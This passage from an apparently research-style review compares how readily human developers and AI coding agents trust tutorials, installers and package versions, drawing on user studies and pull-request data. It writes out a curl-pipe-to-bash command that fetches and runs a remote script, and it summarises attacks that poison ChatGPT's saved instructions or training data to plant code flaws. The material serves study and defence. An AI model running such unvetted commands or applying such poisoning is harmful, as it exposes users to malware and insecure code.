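4. They checked the matches by hand to see which were really vulnerable.

| GitHub stars | Projects | Matches | Vulnerable matches | Vulnerable share of matches | Vulnerable matches per 1,000 projects |
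|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0–3 | 42,064 | 269 | 80 | 30% | 1.9 |
| 4–9 | 16,037 | 528 | 35 | 7% | 2.2 |
| 10 or more | 6,314 | 23 | 2 | 9% | 0.3 |
| Total | 64,415 | 820 | 117 | 14% | 1.8 |

About 80% of the 117 vulnerabilities allowed SQL injection, in which a website puts a visitor's text straight into a database command, letting the visitor add their own commands. Only eight of the 117 were replicas of tutorial code, all from one tutorial on the first page of Google's results.

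The other 109 may be common mistakes. Some templates covered a tutorial's whole snippet, but others covered only the vulnerable lines, which a developer could write without having read that tutorial. One database template matched code that opened a file unsafely, a flaw that nobody could have copied from a lesson on databases. However, the templates missed any copy where the developer had added a line, so there may have been more than eight copies.

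Unruh and colleagues report that the least popular projects had the highest proportion of vulnerable code. That is true as a share of matches, but the two less popular groups had about the same amount per project. Neither figure is a human baseline, because nobody counted the developers who noticed the problem, as was also the case with the misspelled package names. The study is more useful as a measure of exposure, since nearly a third of the top search results included code with a security flaw.

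### Setting up a secure server from online guides

In *I Have No Idea What I'm Doing*, Krombholz, Mayer and colleagues (2017) watched 28 students in a laboratory follow guides to set up a web server with HTTPS, which encrypts the connection between a browser and a website. The students had taken security courses and scored well on an entry quiz, and 17 had done the task before. Each had two hours to make the server as secure as possible for an imaginary audit and could use the web freely.

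Twenty-four participants produced a working setup. Judged by the criteria of a widely used online test, six earned an A or A-minus, 16 a B and two a C. Nearly all the setups graded B had an incomplete chain of certificates, the files that let a browser confirm a site's identity. That reflects a missed step rather than misplaced trust, so the grades are weak evidence about credulity.

Participants visited 60 websites on average, ranging from 20 to 147. Three experienced participants looked for tutorials they already knew. Others often started with one guide, found that it didn't fit the server and switched to another. Twenty-five of the 28 visited a German wiki for Linux users, and 20 visited the server software's official documentation. Visiting more sites made no significant difference to the grade.

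Krombholz and colleagues report that participants who had to choose encryption methods took them from search results and online advice "without questioning". One participant, who never got the server working, admitted not knowing whether the source was trustworthy. The participants were security students whose instructions stressed security, so less knowledgeable people without such instructions would probably question their guides even less.

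Many did test the finished server, however, and Krombholz and colleagues considered repeated testing a key part of a secure setup. People who can't judge a guide's advice on encryption can sensibly test the result instead. This catches honest mistakes, but a hostile command will already have run by the time they test.

The students could also compare dozens of guides, and a strange step in one might have stood out because the others lacked it. An agent that reads only a project's README cannot make this comparison, so a fair test would either let the agent search the web or restrict people to the README. The task has also changed. *A Usability Evaluation of Let's Encrypt and Certbot* (Tiefenau, von Zezschwitz and colleagues) later studied tools intended to make it easier.

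### Comparing a download with its published checksum

Some websites publish a checksum beside a download, a short fingerprint computed from the file's contents that changes if anyone alters the file. In *Towards Usable Checksums*, Cherubini, Meylan and colleagues tested whether people notice when the published checksum doesn't match the downloaded file's.

Researchers asked 40 students from two Swiss universities to download four programs. For each program, the students ran a command to compute the file's checksum, then compared the result with the checksum on the web page. For the third program, the two checksums matched only in the first ten and last ten of their 64 characters. An attacker with enough computing power could produce a malicious file whose checksum matches the published one in those 20 characters.

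Fifteen students (38%; exact 95% interval 23% to 54%) missed the mismatch, although the instructions had told them to compare the checksums. Eye tracking suggested that they had checked less carefully. On the other three downloads, students who caught the mismatch spent about 16 seconds looking at the checksums, and students who missed it spent about four. Students looked most at the first characters and least at the last. Those who already knew what checksums were did no better.

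Comparing only the first few characters of a checksum is a reasonable way to detect a damaged download, because accidental damage would almost certainly change them. It fails only against someone who has deliberately made a file whose checksum starts with the same characters.

Most people don't verify their downloads. In the same paper's survey of 2,000 US internet users, 1.7% said they did, and 5.2% said they would use a checksum if they saw one on a download page. If those 5.2% were as accurate as the students, about 3% of people would catch a mismatch like this one. They would rarely have a checksum to compare, since Meylan and Cherubini later found that only 0.01% of the websites in their sample that linked to programs provided one.

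Cherubini and colleagues also tried a browser extension that compared the checksums automatically, which spared people the tiring work of comparing them by eye. When it warned of a corrupted file, only 40% of the students stopped, and half of those deleted the file. The others mostly said they ignore pop-ups.

An agent can compare two checksums exactly with a single command, so asking it to spot a difference would be too easy a test. A more informative test would measure whether the agent checks a download without being asked, and whether it stops when the check fails.

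### ClickFix and fake installer pages

A checksum doesn't help when an attacker controls the page that displays it, since the attacker can publish one that matches the malicious file. Some attacks don't require the victim to download a program. In an attack called ClickFix, a web page or an email presents a fake problem, such as an error message or a test to prove that the visitor is human, and tells the victim to solve it by pasting a command into a terminal or the Windows Run box.

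MITRE's *User Execution* (2025), part of a widely used catalogue of attack methods, explains that tricking people into running a command can get past email filters and browser protections because the victim runs it personally. It lists Contagious Interview, which targets software developers with fake job interviews, among the campaigns that have used this method. According to Microsoft's *Think before you ClickFix* (2025), the malware often runs in memory and is seldom saved as a program file, so the victim may have nothing to inspect.

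ClickFix attacks have multiplied. The University of Florida's *ClickFix Attacks* reports that those linked to phishing emails quadrupled between May 2024 and May 2025. CybelAngel's *How ClickFix Uses Fake CAPTCHAs to Compromise Users* cites the security company ESET, which recorded 108% more detections in the first half of 2026 than a year earlier. In July 2026, the University of Texas at Austin's *"Prove you're human" just became the attack* warned of a campaign that had hit hundreds of education websites. Recorded Future's *ClickFix Campaigns Targeting Windows and macOS* (2026) identified five clusters of activity and concluded that ClickFix gives attackers a high return.

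These figures describe how active the attackers are, not how easily people fall for the attack. Detections go up when criminals put up more fake pages, even if a smaller share of visitors paste the command. Security companies also publish the share of successful intrusions that began with a given method, but that doesn't measure how easily people fall for it either. Suppose, with invented numbers, that ClickFix started 400 of the 1,000 break-ins a company investigated. Its share would be 40% whether 1,000 people saw the fake pages and 40% of them fell for the attack, or four million saw them and one in 10,000 did. The share would also rise if the company's customers got better at protecting their passwords, because fewer break-ins would begin with stolen ones.

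Most ClickFix pages are also a poor test of developers, who might well notice that no real human-verification test asks anyone to open a terminal. The same request is normal on an installation page.

In TechNadu's *Copy, Paste, Compromise?*, Rhys Downing of the security company Ontinue describes attackers who set up fake installation pages for Claude Code. Developers searching for the product followed links, often sponsored ones, to pages that closely resembled the real documentation. The one-line install command on these pages fetched a script from the attackers' server, and the script stole saved passwords, browser cookies and payment data. Downing does not say how many people saw the pages or ran the command.

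### Running a script straight from the web

One-line installers often look like this:

`curl -fsSL https://get.example.com/install.sh | bash`

The first half of the command downloads a script, and the vertical bar passes it directly to bash, which runs it. The developer doesn't see the script unless they download it separately. Many reputable projects recommend such commands, so running one isn't credulous in itself. The web address is the main clue in the command to whether it can be trusted, and a careful developer would also want to read the script.

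Even these checks can fail. The blogger dstreefkerk (2026) explains in *The curl* that a page can display one command but put a different one on the clipboard when the visitor copies it. If the real company's website has a flaw that lets outsiders redirect its links, a command can show the company's address but fetch the attacker's script. In the fake Claude Code campaign, a developer who opened the script's address directly would have found something that looked harmless.

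People and agents may differ here for reasons unrelated to trust. An agent that reads a page and types the command itself doesn't use the clipboard, so a page that swaps the copied text would fool only people. An agent can also download and read a long script in seconds, while a person may need half an hour. But the agent has to choose to read it, and Claude Opus 4.5 never opened a setup script before running it in the README tests that Ding and colleagues published in April 2026.

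In *Developer Perceptions on Trusting Software*, ElKochta, Spear and colleagues interviewed seven students who had written software professionally. Most said they at least sometimes did nothing to make sure a dependency was secure. All seven said a package's popularity mattered to them, and they judged popularity from mentions on sites such as Reddit and GitHub.

Developers' statements about popularity may not predict what they install. Shen, Sood and Weitzel bought GitHub stars for a random selection of new Python packages and found no discernible effect on downloads. Perhaps developers pay less attention to stars than to recommendations, or few of them came across packages that new.

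### The closest controlled experiments

*I'm regretting that I hit run* (Lit, Crowder and colleagues, 2025) reports the experiment that most closely resembles a decision about an unknown installer. The 36 participants, 11 of them software developers, used laptops that they could safely infect. Imaginary co-workers sent each participant six programs, three of them malicious, and the participant had to decide which were legitimate. Everyone then repeated the exercise with six more programs and a tool that showed what each program was doing, such as which countries it connected to.

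The study reports both hits and false alarms, so the signal detection formulas can be applied to its results. Here a "hit" means calling malware malicious, and the calculation pools all participants' answers.

| | Malware called malicious | Safe software called malicious | Sensitivity d′ | Criterion c |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Without the tool | 88% | 38% | 1.5 | −0.4 |
| With the tool | 94% | 34% | 2.0 | −0.6 |

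The negative criterion means participants leaned towards suspicion. They could tell malware from safe software fairly well, but they rejected more than a third of the safe programs. The tool may have improved their sensitivity, but practice could explain the gain, because everyone used the tool in the second round.

The 88% figure does not measure how often people catch bad installers in ordinary use. Participants knew they were looking for malware, and half the programs were malicious. They could also run a program before judging it. The ransomware encrypted every file on the laptop and changed the desktop background, which made the right answer fairly obvious. Bagmar and Saraf would count a detection at that point as a late warning and score it as a failure. An equivalent figure for people would be the share who rejected each program before running it.

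*Beware EviLLM* (Ryu, Chung and colleagues, 2026) tested something closer to copying and pasting by inserting security flaws into code that people obtained from ChatGPT. When a malicious browser extension made the change, 10 of 13 participants missed the flaws (an exact 95% interval of 46% to 95%). When the attack worked through ChatGPT's saved instructions, 7 of 8 missed them. All participants had programming and security experience. But a subtle flaw in working code is hard to see even when reading every line, whereas an install command may have a visibly wrong address.

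No known controlled study has measured how often developers run an install command from a web page when nothing hints that security is involved. The 15 people who reviewed files for *You Told Me to Do It* did not run anything, and Lit and colleagues' participants were looking for malware. The rate at which developers run such commands without a security cue is the human figure most needed for a comparison with agents that set up projects, because those agents run them routinely.

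A fairly simple experiment could measure how readily developers run installation commands from a fake page. Researchers could give developers a small job that requires an unfamiliar tool, then send half of them to the tool's real installation page and half to a copy at a similar address. Both pages would offer a one-line installer, but the copy's script would only record that it had run. The researchers would note who ran the command without reading the script, who opened the script first, and who refused or found another source. The share of developers who refused the real page's command would be the false alarm rate. Researchers could also give agents the same job and pages.

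The study would need more people than most of those described here. If 8 of 16 developers ran the fake installer, the true rate could be between about 25% and 75%, a range so wide that almost any agent would look normal. If 50 of 100 ran it, the range would narrow to about 40% to 60%.

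## Dependency changes by agents and people in real projects

Running an install command usually leaves no public record, but adding a package to an open-source project does. Contributors usually propose this change to the project's dependency file in a pull request, which others can review before accepting it. Researchers can use pull requests to compare the packages that agents and people choose in ordinary work. *Towards a Benchmark for Dependency Decision-Making* (Singla, Çakar and colleagues, 2026) did this for 2,807 popular GitHub projects. The versions that agents chose were more likely to have known vulnerabilities, but people introduced more vulnerable versions per pull request.

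### What agents and people chose

The pull requests come from AIDev, a public collection of agents' work on GitHub. Singla and colleagues found 117,062 dependency changes in them, counting every package added, removed or moved to another version. They checked each version introduced only for vulnerabilities that were already public when the author submitted the pull request.

| | Agents | People |
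|---|---|---|
| Pull requests | 33,596 | 6,618 |
| Versions introduced | 37,574 | 40,110 |
| Versions with a known vulnerability | 924 (2.46%) | 659 (1.64%) |
| Vulnerable versions that already had a patched alternative | 87% | 83% |
| Vulnerable versions that need a major upgrade to repair | 340 (36.8%) | 85 (12.9%) |
| Changes that fixed a vulnerability | 826 | 1,975 |
| Net effect (fixes minus introductions) | −98 | +1,316 |

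Unlike the agents in Bagmar and Saraf's setup tests, these agents often picked the version themselves. Their choices needed a major upgrade, such as from version 1 to version 2, almost three times as often as people's did. Such an upgrade can break the code that uses the package. The difference may mean that some of the agents' bad choices came from recalling versions in old training data, although the study didn't test this.

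Agents have a worse net effect than people, mostly because people fix more vulnerabilities. Those extra fixes account for 1,149 of the 1,414 difference between the two totals. A developer who spends a week clearing out old packages will fix many vulnerabilities, while an agent asked to add a button will probably fix none. Fixing old problems is valuable, but the number of fixes is weak evidence about credulity.

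### How the unit of counting changes the answer

The same vulnerable versions can make either group look worse.

| Unit | Agents | People | Comparison |
|---|---|---|---|
| Vulnerable versions per 100 versions introduced | 2.5 | 1.6 | Agents 1.5 times higher |
| Vulnerable versions per 100 pull requests | 2.8 | 10.0 | People 3.6 times higher |
| Known vulnerabilities per 100 versions introduced | 6.4 | 3.3 | Agents 2.0 times higher |
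| Critical vulnerabilities per 100 versions introduced | 0.77 | 0.76 | About equal |

The first two rows disagree because people's pull requests introduced about six versions each and agents' only about one:

vulnerable versions per pull request = versions introduced per pull request × share that are vulnerable

Agents made an average of 1.12 choices per request, and 2.46% of those were poor, which gives about 0.028 poor choices per request. People chose poorly somewhat less often, 1.64% of the time, but they averaged 6.06 choices per request, so they made more poor choices per request, about 0.10.

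The last two rows count vulnerabilities instead of versions, since one version can have several. The agents' versions had a total of 2,418 known vulnerabilities, and the people's had 1,309. But 290 of the agents' vulnerabilities were critical, compared with 305 of the people's, so the agents' excess was entirely in less severe vulnerabilities.

The rate per version is the most relevant to credulity because it comes closest to counting decisions. A maintainer deciding how closely to review agents' pull requests may care more about the rate per request, but that rate depends on how people and agents divide their work. If a developer submits a whole feature in one request and an agent splits the same feature into six, the agent looks safer per request even if both chose the same packages. A rate per completed task would avoid this problem, but AIDev doesn't show which requests belong to the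 same task.

### Why a simple significance test would mislead

The usual test for comparing two percentages would treat all 77,684 versions as independent choices. Under that assumption, the difference between 2.46% and 1.64% is about eight standard errors, which chance alone would produce less than once in a trillion comparisons.

But many of these choices were not independent. Someone who starts a project from an old template brings in all its outdated versions, and a large project may list the same package in dozens of dependency files. Twist and Zhang (2026), in *A Study of Library Usage in Agent-Authored Pull Requests*, found similar clustering in AIDev, where only 345 agent pull requests added any packages, but together they added 2,128. A few of these pull requests created entire new projects.

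A small number of such requests could explain the whole difference between agents and people. At the human rate, agents would have introduced about 617 vulnerable versions instead of 924, or about 307 fewer. Thirty requests that each copied about ten vulnerable versions from a template would account for that excess, and they would make up less than 0.1% of the agents' requests.

The correction for repeated reviews by the same person, 1 + (m − 1)ρ, also applies here, with m as the number of versions that arrive together. The difference would no longer be significant if clustering reduced the effective number of choices by a factor of about 17, as it would with batches of 33 versions and a correlation of 0.5. The average request contains far fewer versions, but when batches vary in size, the largest ones affect the correction most.

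A better analysis would resample whole projects instead of single versions, or compare agents and people within the same project. It would also report the share of pull requests with at least one vulnerable version, which one very large request can't distort. Singla and colleagues, who call their study preliminary, report neither a significance test nor a margin of error.

### Differences between the two sets of pull requests

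Singla and colleagues don't know whether agents and people were working on the same tasks or under the same constraints, so they offer the human figures only as "a contextual baseline". Differences in tasks or constraints could explain the whole gap. Suppose, with invented numbers, that 4% of JavaScript versions and 1% of Go versions were vulnerable no matter who chose them. If agents made 49% of their choices in JavaScript, people made 21% of theirs in JavaScript, and the rest were in Go, the overall rates would be about 2.5% for agents and 1.6% for people, even though both groups were equally careful.

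The agents' rate also mainly reflects one product. According to *Security in the Age of AI Teammates* (2026), OpenAI Codex wrote 21,799 of the 33,596 agent requests, while Claude Code wrote 459. The collection ends on August 1, 2025, so the agents date from mid-2025 or earlier. Nobody seems to have repeated the comparison with agents from 2026.

The human group may include a good deal of AI work. AIDev identifies agents by their special accounts, by labels and by information in the commits (the saved changes), so a developer who lets an assistant write the dependency file and then submits it personally would probably count as a person. *Correct Code, Vulnerable Dependencies* (Wang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) cites a 2025 survey in which 51% of professional developers used AI tools daily. Some agents may also have used a version that their user specified. Either kind of mixing would tend to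 make the two groups look more alike than they are.

Bots that update packages automatically could have the opposite effect. *How Humans, Bots, and Agents Communicate About Vulnerabilities in Pull Requests* (2026) separates bots from people in the same projects, but Singla and colleagues don't say whether they did. If some of the "human" requests came from update bots, the 1,975 fixes attributed to people would overstate how many they made themselves.

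A vulnerable version may also be a deliberate choice. In tests that *YUL* describes, agents kept an old version of a Go package because later versions required a newer release of Go than the machine had. Developers may accept a known vulnerability for the same reason, or because it affects a feature they don't use. Pull requests rarely explain such choices, so the data can't distinguish a deliberate choice from a failure to check.

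A pull request is a proposal that maintainers can reject. In Twist and Zhang's data, maintainers accepted 57% of the agent pull requests that added packages, compared with 73% of agent pull requests overall. The package versions in rejected requests are still evidence of what agents choose, but they never reached the project's users.

### How often agents add packages and specify versions

Agents rarely add packages. Twist and Zhang found that, of 26,760 pull requests written by agents in four programming languages, 29.5% imported a library but only 1.3% added a new dependency. They suggest that agents may avoid new packages because agents struggle to install them. Many of the added packages were testing and development tools. The researchers consider this pattern cautious, but a malicious tool can still harm the developer who runs it.

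Twist and Zhang contrast this restraint with typical human practice, but they didn't count people's pull requests. Their count of additions is also hard to reconcile with Singla and colleagues' figures, which imply about 24,000 additions by agents in the same collection, more than ten times as many. Singla and colleagues covered seven package ecosystems, but that alone is unlikely to explain the gap. Twist and Zhang ignored lock files, in which an installer records every package it fetched, including those that other packages require. If the larger count includes lock files, an installer, not an agent, chose many of the packages in it. The smaller count may also be too low, since it lists only nine of 7,480 JavaScript or TypeScript pull requests as adding a dependency.

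When agents did add packages, they specified a version 75% of the time, which Twist and Zhang call good practice. File formats account for part of that rate. Go's dependency file always lists a version, so the 100% rate for Go is not evidence that agents were careful. The rate for C# was 47%.

Specifying a version makes software easier to reproduce, but not necessarily safer. Wang and colleagues gave 1,000 Python questions from Stack Overflow to ten models, including GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 from early 2026. They prompted the models in two ways, asking for either a version in a comment beside each imported library or a separate requirements file.

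| | Libraries given a version | Tasks with at least one vulnerable version |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4, comments | 95% | 46% |
| GPT-5.4, requirements file | 6% | 28% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, comments | 88% | 51% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, requirements file | 15% | 34% |

When a model named no version, the researchers filled in the newest release, as an installer normally would, so both models' code was safer when they left the version out. GPT-5.4 named only about 176 versions in its requirements files, but 281 tasks counted as vulnerable, so in at least 105 of them the known flaw was in the newest release of some library rather than in a version the model chose.

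These rates are far higher than the 2.46% for agents' pull requests, partly because Wang and colleagues used only libraries with at least one recorded vulnerability. They also prompted the models directly, without the tools an agent could use to look up a version. Counting by task also gives a higher rate than counting by library version, because one vulnerable version is enough for a task to count. For Claude Sonnet 4.6 with comments, the rates were 51% of tasks and 39% of library versions.

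The newest evidence concerns outdated versions, which aren't necessarily vulnerable. In autumn 2026, *YUL* gave agents feature requests that didn't mention packages. Claude Opus 5.5 in Claude Code chose a version older than the latest release in 42 of 146 runs (29%), and DeepSeek V4.1 Flash in OpenCode did in 54 of 139 (39%). But 30 of each agent's outdated choices were for GitHub Actions, a service for automating builds, where both agents always wrote version numbers from memory. Without those runs, the rates drop to 10% for Opus and 22% for DeepSeek.

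The agents differed partly in how they vetted dependencies. For Java packages, Opus looked up current versions in 24 of 30 runs and DeepSeek in only 14. DeepSeek could also be too suspicious of accurate warnings, trusting its own outdated memory instead. When the *YUL* tool blocked an outdated version and named the correct one, DeepSeek suspected a planted command in 11 runs, and once insisted that version 7 of a tool didn't exist when it did. Opus followed the same corrections without suspicion, but Claude Code's system prompt tells it to treat such messages as coming from the user.

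### How developers say they choose packages

Wang and colleagues describe the traditional way of picking versions as "a deliberate, human-controlled process" in which developers consult security advisories and changelogs, but developers themselves report being less careful.

Larios Vargas, Aniche and colleagues (2020), in *Selecting Third-Party Libraries*, interviewed 16 experienced developers and then surveyed 115 people about 26 factors drawn from the interviews. Security was highly influential for 39% of respondents, behind maturity and stability (62%), ease of use (55%) and documentation (51%). Only 4% said security had no influence. One interviewee called checking for vulnerabilities important but added, "I do not check it up-front". Others worked at companies where someone else, such as a security team, inspects every new library. A developer who installs a package without vetting it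 may be relying on such a team, so a study that tests developers alone could make a company look more careless than it is.

Developers also weigh security against keeping the software working. Pashchenko, Vu Duc and Massacci (2020) interviewed 25 developers in nine countries for *A Qualitative Study of Dependency Management and Its Security Implications*. They found that teams may not adopt a security fix that comes with breaking changes, because they lack the time to repair their code. People may therefore knowingly keep vulnerable versions, especially when the fix requires a major upgrade.

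Only 24% of the 285 Rust programmers surveyed in *Trusting code in the wild* (Hamer, Imtiaz and colleagues, 2024) said they always or often review a package's incoming code before adding or updating it. Some said reviewing everything was infeasible, and others skimmed the list of changes or trusted the wider community to catch problems. The respondents were active contributors to widely used packages and their dependencies, so 24% may be high for developers in general. The response rate was low (14.3%), and some respondents seem to have misread other questions as asking about changes to their own projects.

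About half (51%) said that contributors' reputations often or always affect how carefully they review, but reputation is a weak safeguard if developers can't remember whose work they have seen. Hamer and colleagues showed respondents the names of people with whom they had a recorded history, including 736 cases in which one had reviewed the other's code. In 12% of those cases, the respondent said they had never heard of the person.

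Even developers who receive security information may not act on it. *What's in a Package?* (Rahman, Paramitha and colleagues, 2024) counted how often Java packages call functions that can reach files, the network or other programs. It also asked developers whether knowing these counts would have changed their choice of a package they already used. Of the 110 who responded, 44.6% said they would consider the information: 24.6% would have selected a package based on it, and 20% would have kept their package and remembered the information for next time. Another 41.8% would not have changed their decision. One explained, "I would assume it does what it does for a reason."

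That assumption is often correct, because a package that fetches web pages has to use the network, but it is also what an attacker would want a developer to think. The answers describe an imagined decision, though. The response rate was only 1.4%, and Rahman and colleagues warn that the answers don't represent developers in general. People who care about security were probably more likely to reply, and may have wanted to sound careful.

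### Stated care and observed choices

Developers may choose a library carefully and then ignore it for years. Almost all of Larios Vargas and colleagues' respondents said security influenced their choice of library, yet *YUL* cites a study in which 81.5% of software systems kept outdated dependencies. A test should therefore compare agents with developers separately on choosing a package, choosing a version and deciding whether to update, because a person may be careful about only one of these.

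The low rate of vulnerable versions in people's pull requests doesn't show that they were careful either, because a developer who types `npm install react` gets the newest release without thinking about security. Agents benefit in the same way. In *YUL*'s tests, neither agent chose an outdated version in any npm or PyPI run, largely because the installers looked up the latest one.

It is therefore useful to compare both agents and people with a simple rule of always choosing a patched version when one exists. In Singla and colleagues' data, agents chose 924 vulnerable versions and people chose 659. About 800 of the agents' choices and 549 of the people's had a patched alternative when the author submitted the request. Following the rule would have cut the rate of vulnerable versions to about 0.3% for both groups. Agents fell further short of that rate than people did, but both groups could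 have avoided most of their vulnerable versions, at least where the patched version would have worked with the rest of the project.

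## How instructions, experience and AI assistance change what developers catch

Pull requests don't show whether anyone asked the author to think about security, how much practice the author had, or which tools they used. In experiments, changing one of these conditions can multiply the share of developers who catch a flaw. Human baselines are therefore hard to interpret without a description of these conditions.

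### Telling reviewers to look for vulnerabilities

Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022), in *Less is More*, asked 150 people, 62% of them software engineers, to review a proposed code change, 160 lines of Java that registered users for a web service. The code had two flaws. After a database error, it wrote the user's email address and unencrypted password to a log file. It also hashed passwords (scrambled them so that the originals are hard to recover) with MD5, which is outdated. The researchers randomly assigned the reviewers to three groups. They didn't mention security to 33 reviewers, told 41 that they were interested in security issues, and told the other 76 the same but also gave them a security checklist.

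*Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (Braz, Fregnan and colleagues, 2021) describes an earlier experiment in which 146 reviewers were given code for managing employees' vacations, again with no mention of security. Eighty of them got a version that allowed SQL injection, and the other 66 got one that accepted negative numbers that users could exploit. After the review, the researchers told everyone that the code contained a vulnerability, without saying what it was, and let those who had missed it look again.

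| Flaw | Found without a mention of security | Found with an instruction or warning |
|---|---|---|
| Password written to a log file (2022) | 1 of 33 (3%) | 19 of 41 (46%) |
| Outdated hash function (2022) | 7 of 33 (21%) | 25 of 41 (61%) |
| Unchecked negative number (2021) | 14 of 66 (21%) | 21 of 66 (32%) |
| SQL injection (2021) | 52 of 80 (65%) | 65 of 80 (81%) |

The 2022 rows compare different people, while the 2021 rows follow the same people and add the flaws they found on the second look.

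Counting both flaws together, reviewers found 12% without the 2022 instruction and 54% with it, about four and a half times as many. Braz and colleagues say the instruction made reviewers eight times more likely to detect a vulnerability, but that figure is a ratio of odds (finds divided by misses). A checklist made no significant difference, even when the researchers cut it to seven items that suited the code.

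The instruction helped most with the flaw that reviewers had missed through inattention. Those who missed the log file flaw without the instruction mostly said they had been concentrating on other things or had overlooked the line. The only reviewer who caught it without the instruction worked at a bank that emails its staff warnings about sensitive data in logs, which had arguably primed them to look for it. The most common explanation for missing the outdated hash function was a lack of knowledge, which an instruction can't supply. Sixteen of the 41 reviewers with the instruction still missed the hash function.

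The choice of flaw mattered as much as the instruction. When reviewers were not told to consider security, detection ranged from 3% to 65%, so a researcher could make the same agent look careful or careless by choosing which flaw to plant. The 2021 code also contained an ordinary bug, and more of the SQL injection group found the vulnerability (65%) than the bug (49%). SQL injection is a textbook attack that many reviewers recognised at once.

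The 2021 warning came with extra time, and no group got a second look without a warning. However, nobody found the ordinary bug on the second look, which suggests that extra time alone didn't lead to the new finds. In the 2022 experiment, 357 of the 522 people who opened it left before the end. If people with little interest in security were more likely to leave when the task mentioned it, the instruction would look more effective than it was.

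Neither experiment included a version of the code without a vulnerability, so some of the improvement may reflect a greater readiness to object.

### Asking for secure password storage

Instructions have a similar effect on people who write code. *Why Do Developers Get Password Storage Wrong?* (Naiakshina, Danilova and colleagues, 2017) studied 20 computer science students, and a follow-up added 20 more. Each student programmed the registration process for a university social network. Of the 20 who were explicitly asked to store passwords securely, 12 did so to some degree, compared with none of the other 20.

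Many of the students who had stored passwords insecurely said they would have taken more care for a real employer. To test this, Naiakshina, Danilova and colleagues (2019), in *If you want, I can store the encrypted password*, hired 43 freelancers for €100 or €200 while posing as a start-up that had just lost its developer. Thirteen of the 21 freelancers they asked for secure storage (62%) provided it in their first submission, compared with four of the 22 they didn't ask (18%). Believing the work was for a real company apparently made little difference.

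When freelancers submitted code that stored passwords in plain text, the "client" asked whether they could also store them securely. Twelve of the 18 who got this message then did so. Most of them could have done it earlier but hadn't treated it as part of the job, and several said that a client who wants security should ask for it.

These rates depend on a generous definition of security. Naiakshina and colleagues counted any hashing as secure, including MD5, which Braz and colleagues treated as a vulnerability. MD5 was used by five of the 13 successful developers who were asked for security and one of the four who were not. If the MD5 solutions counted as failures, the rates would fall to 38% and 14%, and the difference would no longer be statistically significant (p ≈ 0.09). Studies of the same behaviour can therefore report quite different human rates because they score it differently.

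A reminder to be secure doesn't help developers who already believe their code is secure. Some freelancers tried to comply and failed. Eight used Base64, which only rewrites text in different characters and which anyone can reverse. One of them called the result "very tough to decrypt".

These studies bear only indirectly on credulity. They show how strongly people respond to an explicit request for security, but not how readily they accept bad instructions. A developer who stores passwords in plain text has left out a protection that nobody requested, which is different from trusting something harmful by installing software from a stranger's server.

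### Activities that developers don't associate with security

Developers may also fail to recognise that a task affects security. In *Schrödinger's Security* (2020), van der Linden, Anthonysamy and colleagues gave app developers six tasks without mentioning security. These included setting up a programming environment, deciding where to seek help with unfamiliar code, choosing testers and selecting an outside advertising component. The developers treated writing code and using outside components as relevant to security, but largely disregarded security in the other activities.

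The difference between Stack Overflow and the official documentation in the Android experiment showed that where developers look for help can matter a great deal. A developer who writes encryption code carefully may still be careless about choosing a source to learn from.

Following a README involves both adding outside code, which developers associate with security, and setting up a working environment, which they don't. Developers might vet a package when they choose it for an app but not when it is one of 20 that a setup file installs. If so, a human rate measured when developers choose packages would be too cautious a baseline for an agent setting up a project.

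### Students, freelancers and company developers

Students are easier to recruit than professionals, so much of the human evidence comes from them. Naiakshina's doctoral thesis, *Don't Blame Developers!*, compares the students and freelancers with 36 company developers recruited through employers and a German business network. The company developers submitted significantly more secure solutions than the students. They also chose better settings for password storage than the students or freelancers.

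The three groups responded similarly to the experimental conditions. Asking for security improved the results in all of them. Company developers, like students, did better with Spring, a programming framework with built-in support for secure password storage, than with one that left them to arrange it themselves. *Lessons Learned in Five Years of Conducting Security Studies With Software Developers* (Naiakshina, Danilova and Smith, 2022) concludes that students are suitable for studying relative differences in security behaviour, such as whether a request or a framework helps.

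The direction of an effect carries over from one group of developers to another more reliably than its size. The request raised the share of secure solutions by 60 percentage points among students and by 44 among freelancers. In a group that already stored passwords securely 70% of the time, it couldn't raise the share by more than 30 points. A test on students could reasonably show whether a warning about unfamiliar servers helps professionals, but not how often professionals install from such servers.

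Whether agents are unusually credulous depends on absolute rates, so a student baseline can't settle the question. If students are also less careful than company developers when they install packages, comparing agents with students would make the agents look better than they should. *You Told Me to Do It* doesn't resolve this problem, because its 15 participants were mostly graduate students.

Years of experience seem to be a poor way to identify careful developers. In both of Braz and colleagues' experiments, years of professional programming had no significant effect on whether reviewers detected vulnerabilities. Reviewers who said they actively consider vulnerabilities while coding were more likely to find some of them. Java experience made no significant difference among the freelancers, but small samples can easily miss an effect, and Naiakshina and colleagues cite a study of 307 GitHub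 users that did find an effect of programming experience. A baseline study should therefore record how often participants review code and whether security is part of their job, as well as how long they have worked.

The researchers also repeated the freelancer experiment with participants who were told it was a study. They found no significant effect of the earlier deception, though the samples were too small to rule out a moderate difference. This suggests that a baseline study can tell participants they are in a study, as long as it doesn't reveal that it concerns security. In a further study, 44 freelancers reviewed insecure password code instead of writing their own. Asking for security had similar effects, and reviewing took less time, so reviews may be a practical way to study what changes people's behaviour.

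### Writing code with an AI assistant

*Do Users Write More Insecure Code with AI Assistants?* (Perry, Srivastava and colleagues, 2022) compared people who had an AI assistant with people who didn't on security-related programming tasks. Those with the assistant wrote significantly less secure code and were more likely to believe that their code was secure. The assistant ran on codex-davinci-002, a 2022 OpenAI model far older than the coding agents now sold under the name Codex.

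The effect may be smaller in other settings. *Using AI Assistants in Software Development* (2024) describes Perry and colleagues' experiment as five tasks in Python, JavaScript and C, and contrasts it with one by Sandoval and colleagues. In the Sandoval experiment, people who wrote C code with an assistant's suggestions produced only 10% more security bugs than people without an assistant.

These results shouldn't be applied to developers who use an assistant from 2026. A newer model may write safer code than its user would, which would reverse the difference in security. But its users could still be overconfident, and the safer the suggestions usually are, the less reason they have to check each one.

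The security of the finished code is also an imperfect measure of vetting, because the user may have overlooked a flaw the assistant introduced or may have asked for something insecure. Tampering with the assistant allows a more direct test, because the researchers know which suggestions are bad. *Poisoned ChatGPT Finds Work for Idle Hands* (2023) studies developers who receive insecure suggestions from poisoned models, which an attacker has corrupted through their training data. Ryu and colleagues (2026) tampered with ChatGPT in other ways, and most participants missed the inserted flaws.

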